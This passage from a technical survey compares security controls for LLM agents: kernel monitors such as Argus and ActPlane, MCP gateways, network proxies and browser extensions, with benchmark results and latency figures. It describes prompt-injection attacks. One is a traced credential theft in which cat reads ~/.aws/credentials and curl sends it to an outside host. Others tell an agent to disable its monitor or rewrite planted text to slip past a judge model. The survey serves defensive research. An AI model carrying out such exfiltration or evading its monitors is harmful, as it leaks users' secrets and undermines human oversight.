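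These cases show that the combined record can help explain an agent's behaviour. They are weak evidence about security because Zheng and colleagues tested only one attack and did not measure how often the second model would miss attacks or flag ordinary tasks.

AgentSight also does not block actions. The second model runs separately from the agent, so in the README experiment the list of user accounts could have left the machine before the model judged the activity. Zheng and colleagues still present AgentSight as software for recording and reporting. It needs administrator rights on Linux to use eBPF.

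### Permissions from the user's own request

*Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection* (Kashyap, Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues, 2026) describes a monitor called Argus that uses similar probes but can also stop an action. Argus works out what the user's request permits and compares the agent's operations with that, rather than trying to recognise an attack from its wording.

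Argus first has to find the request. It copies the text the harness sends to the model and picks out the parts labelled as the user's. A harness may put a tool's output under the same label, so Argus accepts only text that also reached the agent through its command line, its terminal or another input channel the administrator has chosen. The planted advice on the documentation page arrives over the network, so it can't become part of the request.

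A language model then turns the request into a list of permissions. It reads only the user's words. For "Fix the failing test in ~/proj", it might return this:

```json
{
  "files": [
    {
      "target": "~/proj",
      "rights": ["read", "modify"],
      "evidence": ["Fix the failing test"]
    }
  ],
  "hosts": []
}
```

Argus discards any file or host that does not appear word for word in the request. It also discards a permission to change or delete something unless the model can quote the user's words asking for it. These checks limit the damage if the model makes a mistake.

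Users rarely name everything a task needs, so Argus adds some general permissions. The agent may read and change files in its working folder, but it may delete only files it created during the session. An administrator can add cache folders and approved sites, such as the Python package site `pypi.org`.

Argus immediately allows many operations, including reading files, starting programs and making changes inside the working folder. It is stricter about operations that could affect anything else: sending data over the network, changing files outside the permitted folders, deleting files that existed before the session, and sending signals to processes that do not belong to the agent. A signal is a short message that can, for example, tell a process to stop.

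For most of these riskier operations, an eBPF program looks up the target in a table of permissions. If the table permits the operation, it proceeds. Otherwise Argus freezes the process before the operation takes effect and asks its daemon, which checks the operation in up to three layers:

1. The daemon compares the name of the file with the names in the user's request.
2. It follows any links in the path to find the real file and checks the permissions for that file.
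3. A second language model judges whether the task requires the operation.

For network connections, the daemon also checks whether the address belongs to a permitted host.

The second model receives the user's request, the operation, the programs that led to it and any sensitive files the agent has opened. It can approve the operation only with a confidence of at least 0.7. If the verdict is missing or late, Argus treats the operation as forbidden.

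The type of operation matters. In an example from the paper, a user asks for a summary of a report, and the agent tries to delete the report. Although the request includes the report, the second model refuses the deletion because a summary only requires reading it.

When Argus blocks an operation, it kills the process responsible and its child processes. The agent keeps running, receives the failed command's result and can try another approach. By default, Argus ends the session after ten such interventions, so that an agent following an attacker's instructions cannot test the rules indefinitely.

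### A credential upload, step by step

Kashyap and colleagues illustrate the design with an attack that closely resembles action (b). A user asks an agent to fix a failing test, and text in a file tells the agent to upload a cloud credential. Two standard programs do what the script does in (b): `cat` reads the credential and passes it to `curl`, which contacts the outside host. In simplified form, Argus handles the session like this:

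```text
Program  Operation                     Decision
python   reads src/test_app.py         allowed
python   changes src/app.py            allowed, inside the project
pip      contacts pypi.org             allowed, approved site
cat      reads ~/.aws/credentials      allowed, cat becomes tainted
curl     receives the output of cat    allowed, curl becomes tainted
curl     contacts the outside host     held, then refused
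```

Argus lets `cat` read the credential, because reading sends nothing off the machine. But the file is on a list of sensitive locations, so Argus marks the `cat` process as *tainted*. The mark spreads to `curl` when `curl` receives the output of `cat`.

Argus freezes `curl` when it tries to connect. The outside host is not in the user's request or on the list of approved sites, so the first two layers do not permit the connection. The second model classifies uploading a credential as unrelated to repairing a test. Argus kills `curl`, and the agent can continue the repair.

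In action (b), a single script opens the credentials file and contacts the host. Argus would mark the script itself as tainted and hold its connection in the same way.

A tainted process needs the second model's approval even to contact an approved site such as `pypi.org`, unless the user named that site. This could help with a leak like the one from Claude Cowork. However, reading a file taints the process only if Argus's list covers that file or the file is already tainted, and an administrator may not think to list the ordinary documents in a user's folder.

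The disadvantage is that taint spreads widely and lasts for the rest of the session. A command's output normally goes back to the agent, so the agent and its later commands become tainted too. The second model then has to judge many harmless connections. Liu's restriction on sending data after a sensitive read had the same drawback.

### How well Argus worked

Kashyap and colleagues built a benchmark called ORBIT, in which agents run real shell commands on Linux. It has 126 attack scenarios and 43 ordinary tasks. Each successful attack leaves evidence, such as a marker file, which the benchmark checks for without relying on Argus's alarms. The researchers ran every scenario five times for each model and counted an attack as successful if it worked at least once.

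| Model running the agent | Attacks that succeeded without Argus | Attacks that succeeded with Argus | Ordinary tasks with a false alarm |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1 | 97.3% | 38.9% | 0.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 55.9% | 27.9% | 4.7% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 8.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GLM-5.2 | 56.8% | 36.9% | 27.9% |

Argus helped with every model, but more than a quarter of attacks still succeeded against three of the four. Attacks that the model itself refuses to carry out also count as stopped, so the perfect result for Claude Opus 4.7 is due more to the model than to Argus. The GPT-5.1 result is a better measure of Argus's contribution, because without Argus that model followed nearly every malicious instruction.

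The results for separate groups of attacks imply that most of these totals leave out 15 scenarios in which the agent is told to shut down the monitor. Including them raises the rate without Argus to about 19% for Claude Opus 4.7 and by about five percentage points for Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GLM-5.2, but hardly changes the rates with Argus. None of the attempts disabled Argus, which runs under a separate account outside the agent's control.

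Argus was most effective when an attack did something unusual for the task. With GPT-5.1, it stopped every attack that planted commands in documentation or in the logs of an automated build, and 73.3% of attempts to steal credentials.

Argus was weakest when an attack looked like normal work. Three groups of attacks used local files, search results and web pages, and caused operations that agents carry out all the time. In tests with GPT-5.1, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GLM-5.2, Argus and the models together stopped only 20% to 46.7% of the attacks in these groups. This is another example of the semantic gap, because the kernel records a request to a website, but many legitimate tasks also involve a request to a website that the user never named.

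GLM-5.2's false alarms had a similar cause. They were concentrated in web tasks and in tasks where the agent had to find out which site to contact. In the group that used web pages, all five ordinary tasks caused a false alarm, and 80% of the attacks still succeeded. The agents completed nearly all their tasks despite the alarms, probably because Argus killed one command at a time and they could try something else.

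ORBIT also includes attacks that place the malicious instruction in the user's own request. With GPT-5.1, 93.3% of these succeeded despite Argus, which is expected because Argus takes its permissions from the request. Argus would probably have been a poor defence in Anthropic's February exercise, where the employee's own prompt contained the malicious instruction.

Six further scenarios tested Argus's rules for network connections. Half of these attacks succeeded with every model except Claude Opus 4.7. Six scenarios are too few to give a reliable success rate, but the result suggests that Argus might not do as well against attackers who had studied it.

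Kashyap and colleagues compared Argus with CaMeL, which restricts an agent's plan and tool calls before they run. With GPT-5.1, CaMeL stopped 54.8% of attacks and Argus stopped 61.1%. The difference in task completion was larger, with agents completing 77.0% of tasks with CaMeL and 98.2% with Argus.

OpenAI and Anthropic have released newer models than those tested, which may refuse more of the attacks. In Liu's experiments, GPT-6.1 Sol never attempted an attack. But a model can refuse only an attack it detects, and a tool or test script that contains hidden code may show no sign of one.

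### Limits that a person authorises

Argus works out permissions automatically, which is convenient, but the permissions can be wrong. Other kernel monitors, including *ActPlane* (2026), rely on rules that someone has written or approved. *ActPlane* also explains its refusals to the agent. *ContractWarden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) makes a person responsible for the limits on each task.

Someone first lists the files and folders that need protection. Before the task starts, a model may suggest one of three settings for each, but a person makes the final choice:

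- `allow` adds no restriction.
- `deny` blocks access to the file, including attempts to change, rename or delete it.
- `no_egress` lets a process read the file, but that process can no longer send anything over the network.

ContractWarden starts the task's first process but keeps it waiting until these settings are in force, so that the process cannot act before the monitor is ready.

In action (b), a person might choose `no_egress` for the credentials file. The script could open the file, but ContractWarden would then stop it from contacting any host. The restriction spreads to processes the script starts, files it writes, and other processes that read those files. ContractWarden checks a network connection when a process creates it and again when the process sends data, so the script could not send the credentials over a connection it opened before reading them.

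Nothing inside the task can lift the restriction, and no model takes part in enforcing it, so planted text cannot persuade a model to relax it once the task is running. However, ContractWarden cannot permit some destinations and block others. An agent that legitimately needs a credential to update a cloud service could not use it under `no_egress`, so the person would have to choose `allow`, which gives no protection.

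Cui and colleagues tested 19 security properties of ContractWarden 30 times each, and all 570 runs passed. The tests checked, for example, whether a restriction survives when data passes through another file and whether a failed setup keeps the task from starting. The results are good evidence that the mechanism works as designed on the tested paths. They do not show how many attacks on a real agent it would stop, because the tests used prepared programs and fixed settings.

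The result also depends on people making good choices. ContractWarden does not protect a file that nobody listed, and it applies an `allow` setting even if someone chose it carelessly. Approval fatigue is a reason to doubt that people would study every setting before every task. Deciding once before a task may be easier than answering prompts throughout it, but Cui and colleagues have not tested this with users.

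### Trusting a second model

Instead of asking a person, a monitor can let a second model decide the uncertain cases. Hempel and colleagues measured what the second model contributes in Kairos by making the system refuse every action that its fixed rules did not settle. The agent then completed 42.7% of ordinary tasks, down from 85.1%, while the share of attacks that succeeded stayed about the same.

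On AgentDojo, the second model made the agent much more useful without a measurable loss of security. But AgentDojo gave Kairos ready-made tool calls, and a monitor that receives only file and network operations has less information. Hempel and colleagues acknowledge that rules about such operations can express only some of what rules about tool calls can. The fixed rules therefore decide fewer cases, and the second model has to decide more.

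It is difficult to decide how much context to give the second model. Joos and Pradel give theirs a lot. Their monitor, AgentBouncer, uses seccomp rather than eBPF to pause system calls before they run. It handles routine calls using fixed rules and earlier decisions. For the rest, a second model receives the user's task, the tool call and the agent's explanation for making it, then judges whether the system call is necessary and whether it is safe. AgentBouncer allows a clearly safe call even if its purpose is not yet clear, but blocks an unsafe one however useful it seems.

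Joos and Pradel tested AgentBouncer on 340 attacks with GPT-5.6 Luna, a newer model than the GPT-5.1 used in Argus's test. The attacks came through planted instructions, malicious tools, planted scripts and test suites with hidden code. AgentBouncer reduced the share of attacks that succeeded from 99.41% with no control to 10.59%, and the agent completed about as many ordinary tasks as without it.

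That result is better than Argus's, but the benchmarks differ too much for a direct comparison. Many of Joos and Pradel's attacks damaged system files or opened connections that a software repair would not need. Such actions are easier to recognise as harmful than a web request that could belong to the task.

The agent's explanation can help the second model understand an unexpected but legitimate step, but it can also mislead that model, since planted text that has influenced the agent may shape the explanation too. Argus therefore never treats anything the agent writes as authorization. Kashyap and colleagues point out that a model often repeats the targets named in planted text, so that text could otherwise supply the approval for the action it requests. This leaves Argus with less evidence when an agent has good reason to contact a site that the user did not mention.

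Text from an attacker can reach the second model even without the explanation. Argus gives its second model file paths and command arguments, which may contain an attacker's words, and prompts it to treat any instructions in them as signs of an attack. Kairos gives its second model the untrusted content behind an action, because the model needs that content to decide.

Hempel and colleagues tested this weakness by having a model rewrite the planted text over six rounds to get past Kairos. The attacks succeeded in 8.8% of cases, compared with 52.4% without a defence. The successful attacks involved tasks in which the user had told the agent to follow a document. Kairos's second model took the document's instructions to be the user's own, much the same mistake that makes agents vulnerable to prompt injection.

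Designers can limit the damage from such a mistake. In Kairos, the second model cannot overrule an explicit prohibition, and Kairos and Argus both treat a missing answer as a refusal. An administrator should therefore put the most important limits in fixed rules and leave the second model to decide cases where an occasional error is tolerable.

Kernel monitors have narrowed the semantic gap most for actions that clearly go beyond the request, such as sending an unmentioned credential to an unmentioned host. They have done much less about harmful actions that use the access a task requires. Kashyap and colleagues exclude these from Argus's guarantees, such as writing incorrect content to a file the user asked the agent to edit. In the running example, Argus would hold an attempt to delete the failing test, because the file existed before the session, but would allow the agent to rewrite the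 test so that it always passed.

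## Which actions does each placement miss?

The table compares how typical controls, one at each placement, register the four actions in the running example. The controls are an MCP proxy, a browser extension, a network proxy that decrypts TLS, and a kernel monitor. "With meaning" means that the control receives the operation and its target in a form that a rule can use, such as a file's path or a recipient's address. "Without meaning" means that the control registers an event but cannot determine from it what the agent did.

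| Action | Protocol boundary | Browser | Network traffic | Operating system |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| (a) A local MCP server reads a configuration file | Seen with meaning | Not seen | Not seen | Seen with meaning |
| (b) A script opens a credentials file and contacts an outside host | Not seen | Not seen | Seen with meaning (upload only) | Seen with meaning |
| (c) The agent submits a form in the browser | Seen without meaning | Seen with meaning | Seen with meaning | Seen without meaning |
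| (d) A remote service shares a document with an outsider | Seen with meaning | Not seen | Seen with meaning | Seen without meaning |

Even "with meaning" doesn't include the reason for an action, so the semantic gap remains in every cell.

The network proxy misses (a) because the harness and a local server exchange messages over standard input and output. If the proxy also decrypts traffic between the agent and its model, it can find the model's request for the file and later the file's contents, but it still has no record of the read itself.

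For (d), a monitor in the laptop's kernel can detect only a connection. The sharing happens in the service's data centre, so no monitor on the laptop can observe it, whatever its privileges. A probe on the encryption library could recover the text of the request, but the monitor would then have to interpret an MCP message, as a proxy does.

Controls at the protocol boundary have the opposite weakness. An MCP proxy misses the script in (b), and a hook in the harness receives only the command that starts the script.

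Without decryption, the three "with meaning" cells in the network column would all become "without meaning".

No single placement covers all four actions and captures what they mean. The protocol boundary and the operating system together cover (a), (b) and (d), so the form (c) needs a control in the browser or on the network. How much each gap matters depends on how agents usually work.

### How often agents act outside MCP

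*SWE-chat* (Baumann, Padmakumar and colleagues, 2026) collected logs of almost 18,000 sessions in which developers worked with coding agents on public projects. By September 2026 the logs contained 1,996,558 tool calls. Only 1.4% went to MCP servers that users had installed, more than 45% were shell commands, and another 31% went to the harness's own tools for reading, editing and writing files.

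Agents ran network programs such as `curl` and `ssh` in 1.6% of calls, slightly more often than they called MCP tools. A hook in the harness could have checked nearly all of the calls in the logs, but about 6% ran build software or language interpreters such as `npm` and `python`. For those, the command identifies the program but gives little indication of what it will do.

The sample is not typical of all agents. It includes only developers who chose to publish their logs, about 69% of the sessions used Claude Code, and about 16% came from the company that makes the logging software. Office agents probably use MCP more. A count of calls also does not measure their importance, since one call that shares a confidential document can do more harm than thousands that list files.

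Attaching the right MCP servers does not ensure that agents will use them for this work. In *The Scaffolding Matters More Than the Interface*, Alier Forment, Casañ Guerrero and colleagues (2026) had agents carry out tasks in a public GitHub repository with GitHub's MCP server attached. Of 21 runs, 6 used only the MCP tools and 6 used only shell commands. In 4 others, the agent bypassed both and sent requests directly to GitHub's web API. Telling the agents which interface to use made no material difference.

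Removing the credentials that made the other routes work did help. In the main experiment, the MCP server had its own credential and the agent's shell had none. Of the 17 MCP runs with a record of tool calls, 11 used only MCP tools, but 2 still used no MCP tools. Servers that accept connections only from the proxy work the same way, keeping the agent on the intended route by making the alternatives fail.

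*CodeCompass* (2026) also found that agents often ignore instructions about tools. Its agents had an MCP tool for looking up how parts of a program depend on one another, and explicit instructions to call it before editing any file. They never called it in 51 of 88 trials. A better-formatted prompt increased use on some tasks but not on others.

Agents also have good reason to use the shell. *Is Bash All You Need?* (Mak, Suresh and colleagues, 2026) compared ways of giving agents access to the same office work. On tasks in a simulated software company, agents with only a shell scored 67% to 69%, while those with only a catalogue of specialised tools scored about 45%. Shell-only agents also scored 5 to 7 percentage points higher on tasks from banking, consulting and law. They used fewer tokens in every comparison, and adding the catalogue to the shell brought no detectable gain.

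Mak and colleagues recommend giving agents a shell if the company can isolate the code they run. Where compliance rules require a fixed catalogue of tools, they suggest letting the model write short programs that can act only through those tools, so that a control can check every action as a tool call. In the simulated company, agents scored 16 to 22 percentage points lower with this arrangement than with a shell. The catalogue may explain part of the difference, because the researchers had to build it for this benchmark. Still, companies that want every action to pass through the protocol boundary can expect agents to accomplish less.

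Even when an action goes through MCP, its effects can be unclear, because an MCP server can offer a tool that runs code. *APEX-Harm* (Yang, Bibi and colleagues, 2026) gave agents MCP servers for email, calendars, documents, spreadsheets and running code, and the agents mainly used the code tools. A gateway would receive such a call with a whole program as its argument, and would have to predict what the program would do.

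*LEANGUARD* (2026) checks tool calls against formally verified rules. In tests on customer-service tasks, it allowed no calls that its rules forbade. But it treats shell commands as tools whose effects it cannot determine. A control with this limitation has to refuse harmless commands or allow some that it cannot assess.

### A withdrawn claim of complete mediation

Designers can also overestimate what their controls cover. *Governed MCP* (Son, 2026) moved the gateway for tool calls into the kernel of an experimental operating system so that an agent could not switch it off. Agents ran in a sandbox and could reach the rest of the system only through 15 functions, each of which called the gateway first.

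Son listed 123 paths from an agent to the system and ran a program that checked whether each one passed through the gateway. All 123 did. Son presented the result in April 2026 as evidence of complete mediation, though only for the sandbox's own interface.

Son withdrew that result in a July revision. In the new count, 43 of 59 paths passed through the gateway. The other 16 included six system calls for storing and fetching data and for exchanging messages. Son now limits the claim to the sandbox's functions and the MCP tools, and plans to bring the six calls under the gateway later.

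The original list came from the definition of the interface that the gateway guarded. Son's program worked through each function's possible arguments and errors, so it could produce many paths, but all of them went through that interface. A perfect score was therefore almost guaranteed.

The same mistake is easy to make with an ordinary MCP gateway. Its log might show that it checked every MCP call, even though the agent did most of its work in the shell. A better test is to list every way an agent could reach what needs protection, such as the credentials file, the network and the document service, then try each route and confirm that the control intervenes.

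### What project rules require

Coverage also depends on the rules people want to enforce. Many software projects keep instructions for coding agents in a file usually called `CLAUDE.md` or `AGENTS.md`. *ActPlane* collected 84 of these files from 64 popular projects in May 2026 and divided them into 2,116 statements. Language models labelled the statements, and people checked a sample of 100.

About 64% of the statements were policies, meaning they required, forbade or set conditions on something the agent does. The rest described the project. Of the 1,361 policies, 83% concerned something observable in the computer system. The others concerned things like how the agent explains its work.

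The 83% overstates what a kernel monitor can enforce, because it includes policies about the contents of files, such as rules on coding style. These made up 38% of all policies, and the researchers leave them to other software. Another 29% concerned a single event, such as a forbidden command, and 16% required a record of several events, for instance to check that the agent ran the tests before it saved a version of the project.

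Only 26.4% of the observable policies included everything a control would need. "Never push to main directly" is specific enough, but "Run the full test suite before committing" doesn't specify which command runs the tests. About 64% required this kind of knowledge of the project, and 9% depended on the current task, such as whether the user had approved a change. Of all the policies, about 22% were both observable and specific enough to turn directly into a rule.

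Missing context is a problem at every placement, because an MCP proxy or a hook would also need to know which command runs the tests. These files mostly concern good development practice, so a company's security rules might be more specific. But a security product's fixed list of rules would cover only a small part of what these projects ask of their agents.

### How ActPlane turns instructions into kernel rules

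ActPlane has an agent supply the missing context. The agent reads the project and writes the policies in a small rule language, and a compiler prepares them for an eBPF engine in the kernel. For the project in the running example, a rule about tests might look like this:

```text
kill exec "git" "commit"
  if AGENT unless after exec "pytest" exits 0
  since write "**/*.py"
  because "Run pytest before committing."
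```

The engine kills a `git commit` started by the agent unless the test program `pytest` has finished successfully since the last change to a Python file. The rule applies to every process that descends from the agent, whether the model requested the commit directly or a script ran it. When the engine kills a commit, the agent receives the text after `because`.

A rule can also block an operation before it happens or just notify the agent. Blocking is safer for a deletion, because `kill` acts only after the operation. The engine labels data and tracks it between processes, files and connections, much as Argus spreads taint, so a rule can depend on what a process has read.

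ActPlane fixes some rules before the agent starts, because letting an agent write its own rules would be dangerous if it could also relax them. The agent can add stricter rules for itself and the processes it starts, but it cannot remove or weaken the fixed ones. At worst, planted text could make the agent drop the rules it had added.

An agent running GPT-5.5 translated all 607 policies that the engine could in principle enforce, and only two needed a second attempt to compile. This shows that a model can use the language, but a rule that compiles may still be too broad or too narrow. A rule about `git` also doesn't apply to a different program that does the same job.

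### Kernel rules against tool-call checks

The researchers then compared ActPlane with controls at the protocol boundary. They chose 38 policies from 15 projects and had an agent prepare five *traces*, or recorded work sessions, for each. Two complied with the policy. The other three broke it in different ways: through a direct tool call, a script the agent had written earlier, or an effect hidden behind a harmless-looking command.

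The evaluation used 190 traces, 114 of which contained violations. The researchers replayed each trace with a control in place and let an agent continue for up to five steps. A result counted as correct if the agent corrected a violation, or if it continued permitted work without the control wrongly interfering. The researchers used a language model to judge the outcomes.

Three of the controls acted on tool calls. The prompt filter used a language model to approve or refuse each call. The pattern matcher looked for forbidden text, as simple hooks do. FIDES tracked how data moved from one tool call to the next. The researchers also ran ActPlane without its explanations, so the agent was told only that an operation had failed.

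| Control | Correct results (of 190) | Violations corrected (of 114) | Permitted traces disrupted (of 76) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt filter | 48.4% | 44 | 28 |
| Pattern matcher | 45.3% | 38 | 28 |
| FIDES | 48.9% | 41 | 24 |
| ActPlane without explanations | 53.7% | 27 | 1 |
| ActPlane | 75.8% | 86 | 18 |

The controls performed about equally well on direct violations and permitted work. ActPlane's advantage came mainly from the scripts and the hidden effects. On hidden effects, the three tool-call controls scored near zero because, as with action (b), the forbidden operation took place inside a subprocess or behind a harmless-looking command.

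The score reflects both how well a control detects violations and how well it gets the agent to correct them. ActPlane detected 77.2% of violations, and nearly as many (75.4%) without explanations. The tool-call controls detected only 34% to 40%. These detection rates are more useful than the overall scores for choosing a placement, and they show a larger advantage for the kernel.

Agents corrected 97.7% of the violations that ActPlane detected and explained, but only 31.4% of those that ended in an unexplained failure. A security team may still count an upload that fails without explanation as a success, since the data has not left. But when a policy requires the agent to do something, such as run the tests, the agent has to learn what to do instead.

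Explanations may also disrupt permitted work. ActPlane disrupted 18 of the 76 permitted traces when it gave explanations, compared with one when it did not. Nearly all of the 18 disruptions came from rules that were too broad. The difference may have arisen because agents ignored unexplained failures but obeyed mistaken explanations and gave up permitted work.

The researchers built this benchmark themselves, and its design favours kernel controls. They included only policies that ActPlane's engine could enforce, and tool-call controls are known to miss two of the three kinds of violation tested. No test was designed around effects inside a remote service, where tool-call controls might catch more than kernel controls. The result is good evidence that tool-call controls miss what happens inside scripts, but it does not show how often agents break rules that way in ordinary work.

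The researchers repeated the test with another model, DeepSeek V4 Pro. ActPlane scored 77.4% and the ranking stayed the same, so the result does not depend on a single model. They also let the rule-writing agent revise its rules after studying the 28 violations that ActPlane had failed to correct. The revised rules handled 26 of them, raising detection to 94.7%. But because the agent had seen evidence from those same traces, the improvement is little evidence of how well the rules would handle new violations.

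Another test used tasks from OctoBench, a benchmark of how well coding agents follow instructions. Only 21 of its 217 tasks contained a requirement that ActPlane could enforce, which also suggests that many requirements can't be enforced at the operating system level. On those 21 tasks, ActPlane raised the score for following the user's request by 9.9 percentage points compared with an agent without it.

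### Unsafe requests and effects in remote services

The researchers' last test used 361 workplace tasks from an outside benchmark, OpenAgentSafety. Completing these tasks requires an unsafe action, such as sending out credentials, tampering with financial records or wiping a system's configuration. For each task, a model wrote rules based on its description, and ActPlane loaded them before the agent started.

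Without ActPlane, 106 tasks ended in an unsafe outcome. ActPlane prevented 78 of these, leaving 28. It also intervened in 16% of the tasks that were safe without it, typically because a harmless operation came close to what a rule prohibited. That rate would be high for everyday work.

People other than the control's developers built OpenAgentSafety, so the test is less likely to have been designed to suit the control. But the model could write useful rules because the task descriptions often named the dangerous file or command. For 58 of the 361 tasks, it found nothing specific enough to write a rule about. In the running example, the developer only asks the agent to fix a failing test, and nothing in the request suggests that the agent will look for credentials. Rules written from that request alone could easily omit credentials.

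The 28 remaining failures were of three kinds. In some, the harm was in a chat message the agent wrote, which left nothing for the kernel to check. In others, the agent wrote harmful content to a file. The rest took effect inside a service, for example through a file upload or a database change. In these last cases, the model had written a rule against the harmful outcome, but the agent achieved it by a route that the kernel engine did not monitor.

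The last group resembles action (d), which an MCP proxy can refuse before the service acts. But if the agent sends the same request from a script, the company would need to decrypt the traffic or have the service enforce the rule.

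## What does each placement cost, and what new risks does it bring?

Covering all four actions in the running example takes at least two controls. Each one is another program that can slow the agent, fail or be taken over by an attacker. The table compares what each placement adds to a machine and lists sandboxes and kernel monitors separately because they need very different privileges.

| Placement | What it adds | Privilege it holds | Harm if an attacker takes it over |
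|---|---|---|---|
| Protocol boundary | A proxy and a changed entry in the harness's configuration | Usually an ordinary account, often with credentials for the servers behind it | Use of every connected service |
| Browser | An extension | Access to pages on the sites it covers | Theft of logged-in sessions, altered pages |
| Network traffic | A proxy, a root certificate on each device and a forced route | The power to imitate websites to those devices | Reading and changing all inspected traffic |
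| Operating system: sandbox | Little beyond the harness | Usually the user's own | Commands regain the user's full access |
| Operating system: kernel monitor | Programs in the kernel and a daemon | Administrator rights | Observing and blocking across the whole machine |

Even a small security component can have a lot of power. A root certificate is a small file, but whoever holds the matching private key can imitate almost any website to the devices that trust it. An MCP proxy may need no special rights on its own machine and still hold the database credential, as in Millstone and colleagues' design. Keeping the credential in the proxy protects it from a manipulated agent but makes the proxy a more valuable target.

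### Measured delays

Researchers have measured the delay that several of these controls add, but the results don't allow a direct ranking. None of the studies below timed a browser extension.

| Control | What the researchers timed | Added delay |
|---|---|---|
| Liu's gateway | A file copy that takes 2.28 ms without a control | 0.03 to 0.10 ms |
| HCP, Liu's centralised system | The same file copy | 0.26 to 0.31 ms |
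| Kairos's network proxy | One web request | About 1.2 ms |
| AgentSight | Studying a code repository, writing code, compiling | 3.4%, 4.9%, 0.4% |
| ActPlane with 32 rules | Replayed agent work | 1.9% |
| ActPlane with 32 rules | Building the Linux kernel | 6.5% |
| ActPlane with 100 rules | The same two workloads | Up to 8.4% |
| Argus | Attaching to a running agent | 21.2 ms, once |

Liu ran the file copy 1,000 times per configuration, in two passes, with the same server and inputs each time. Forwarding a web request was slower, at about 33 ms, and the differences between controls on that task were no larger than the variation between passes.

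HCP had a clearer effect on memory use, which grew by 7.7 MB over 1,000 file copies because HCP kept a record of every task and decision. Memory use grew by 0.7 MB with the gateway, the same as with no control. A company running HCP for weeks would have to move those records out of memory, which Liu's version does not do.

The AgentSight figures are less certain. Zheng and colleagues timed Claude Code on each task three times with the monitor and three times without it. The slowest task took 128.0 seconds without the monitor and 132.3 seconds with it. Much of that time was probably spent waiting for the model, whose response time varies, so three runs are too few to reliably distinguish a few seconds of monitoring from a slow reply. The figures also exclude the time AgentSight's second model takes to produce a verdict.

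*ActPlane* avoids the first problem by replaying a fixed series of 68 tool actions. But its rules never fired during these tests, so the figures leave out the time an agent spends recovering from a refusal. With 100 rules, the monitor increased the time to open a file from 0.58 to 13.4 microseconds, which would add only about 0.13 seconds to a command that opened 10,000 files.

Argus's 21.2 milliseconds covers only attaching the monitor at the start of a session. Kashyap and colleagues call the overhead "operationally invisible", but they don't report how long Argus holds operations while checking them. Some of those operations wait for a reply from a second language model, which almost certainly takes much longer than attaching the monitor. Argus reuses a verdict when the same kind of operation recurs in a session, so the first upload to an unfamiliar host would be slower than later ones.

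### Why the model hides most local delay

In each round, an agent waits for the model to choose an action and then for the tool to carry it out. A check's effect on the total is roughly:

```text
share of time added = added delay / (model time + tool time)
```

In Liu's tests, GPT-6.1 Sol took a median of 4.6 seconds per request. A call to a simulated tool took 0.39 milliseconds without a control and 0.57 milliseconds through HCP. HCP therefore made the tool call nearly 50% longer, but added only about 0.004% to the combined time of the model request and tool call.

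The same reasoning explains the gap between ActPlane's two results. An agent pauses to wait for the model, whereas a kernel build opens files and starts processes continuously. If an agent starts a ten-minute build, the monitor might add about 40 seconds at the measured overhead of 6.5%, because the agent makes no model requests during the build that would hide the delay. Faster models would also make local delays more noticeable.

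A check that calls another model is different because, like the agent, it has to wait for a model to respond. Kairos's placeholder replies can hide some of that wait, but Argus has no equivalent. A permission prompt can take even longer because someone has to notice it.

### When a gateway makes the model slower

A gateway can also change how much text the model must read. Zheng and colleagues measured this with GPT-5.4 in GATEWAYBENCH for flattened gateways, which list every tool, and hierarchical gateways, which make the model look up tools.

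| Measurement | Flattened | Hierarchical |
|---|---|---|
| Tokens per turn, no extra tools | 8,300 | 9,100 |
| Tokens per turn, 1,500 extra tools | 233,300 | 12,600 |
| Time per task, no extra tools | 20.8 seconds | 30.1 seconds |
| Time per task, 1,500 extra tools | 64.1 seconds | 38.7 seconds |

Looking up tools takes more time than it saves when there are few of them, but starts to save time somewhere between 500 and 1,000 extra tools. These differences of many seconds per task are far larger than the fractions of a millisecond in Liu's test, but most of the time difference comes from the tool lists rather than security checks. A harness that connected directly to the same servers and gave the model every tool description would be slowed about as much.

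Products of the same design also differed in speed. An average tool call took about 0.1 seconds through Bifrost and 0.2 seconds through Strata, but between 2.6 and 5.4 seconds through Enkrypt, which returned long listings on each lookup. These listings waste tokens and put Enkrypt's guardrail settings and connection parameters into the context of the agent that Enkrypt is supposed to restrain.

### Failing open and failing closed

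A control *fails open* if work continues unchecked when the control breaks, and *fails closed* if the work stops. Failing open keeps people productive, but an attacker who can crash the control can bypass it. Failing closed prevents that, but a fault in the control then interrupts everyone who depends on it.

Argus treats a missing verdict as a refusal, so it fails closed for risky operations. If its daemon exits, the processes it was holding stay frozen. If the buffer that carries events to the daemon fills up, its kernel component refuses any risky operation it cannot record, so an attacker cannot get an upload past Argus by flooding it with events. But an outage at the second model's provider would also block legitimate uploads that only that model could approve.

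Claude Code's sandbox fails open by default if it cannot start. Microsoft's toolkit fails closed if a rule causes an error, but open if nobody has loaded any rules.

Whether a proxy fails closed also depends on the rest of the machine. If an MCP proxy crashes, calls through it fail, but the agent still has its shell and may look for an unchecked route. Likewise, a network proxy fails closed only if the operating system blocks every connection that bypasses it.

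A browser extension often fails open. If its page script stops running, the page still loads and the form still submits. Request rules are more robust because the browser applies them itself. For any placement, an administrator can learn more about how the control fails by switching it off and trying a forbidden action than by reading the product's description.

### A gateway flaw that gave access to the host

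Some failures give an attacker more power than the agent had. GitLab's *CVE-2026-55887* (18 June 2026) describes one in Docker's MCP Gateway. The gateway starts MCP servers in containers, which normally limit what a server can reach. It built the command that started each container using text from the image's label, without checking that text properly. A malicious image could change the command to open the host's files and run code on the host as *root*, the account with full administrative power.

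The advisory rates the flaw 8.6 out of 10. It affected versions from 0.21.0 until Docker fixed it in 0.42.2. Zero Day Initiative's *Docker MCP Plugin OCI Image Label Parsing Argument Injection Remote Code Execution* (2026) says the flaw was reported to Docker on 20 May and that an attack would require the victim to refer to the malicious image. According to GitLab, the image could also come from a catalogue the victim used. Neither advisory mentions an actual attack.

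Rules about tool calls would not have helped, because the harm could occur when the server started, before the agent called any of its tools. A proxy that only forwards messages to remote servers does not need permission to start containers, so a flaw in it would probably do less damage to the host, though it could still expose the credentials the proxy holds.

A gateway's risk also depends on how it receives messages. GitLab's *CVE-2025-64443* (2025) describes an earlier flaw that let a malicious website operate the tools behind the same gateway if the gateway accepted network connections. The default mode, which uses standard input and output, did not have this flaw.

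### Security extensions that exposed their users

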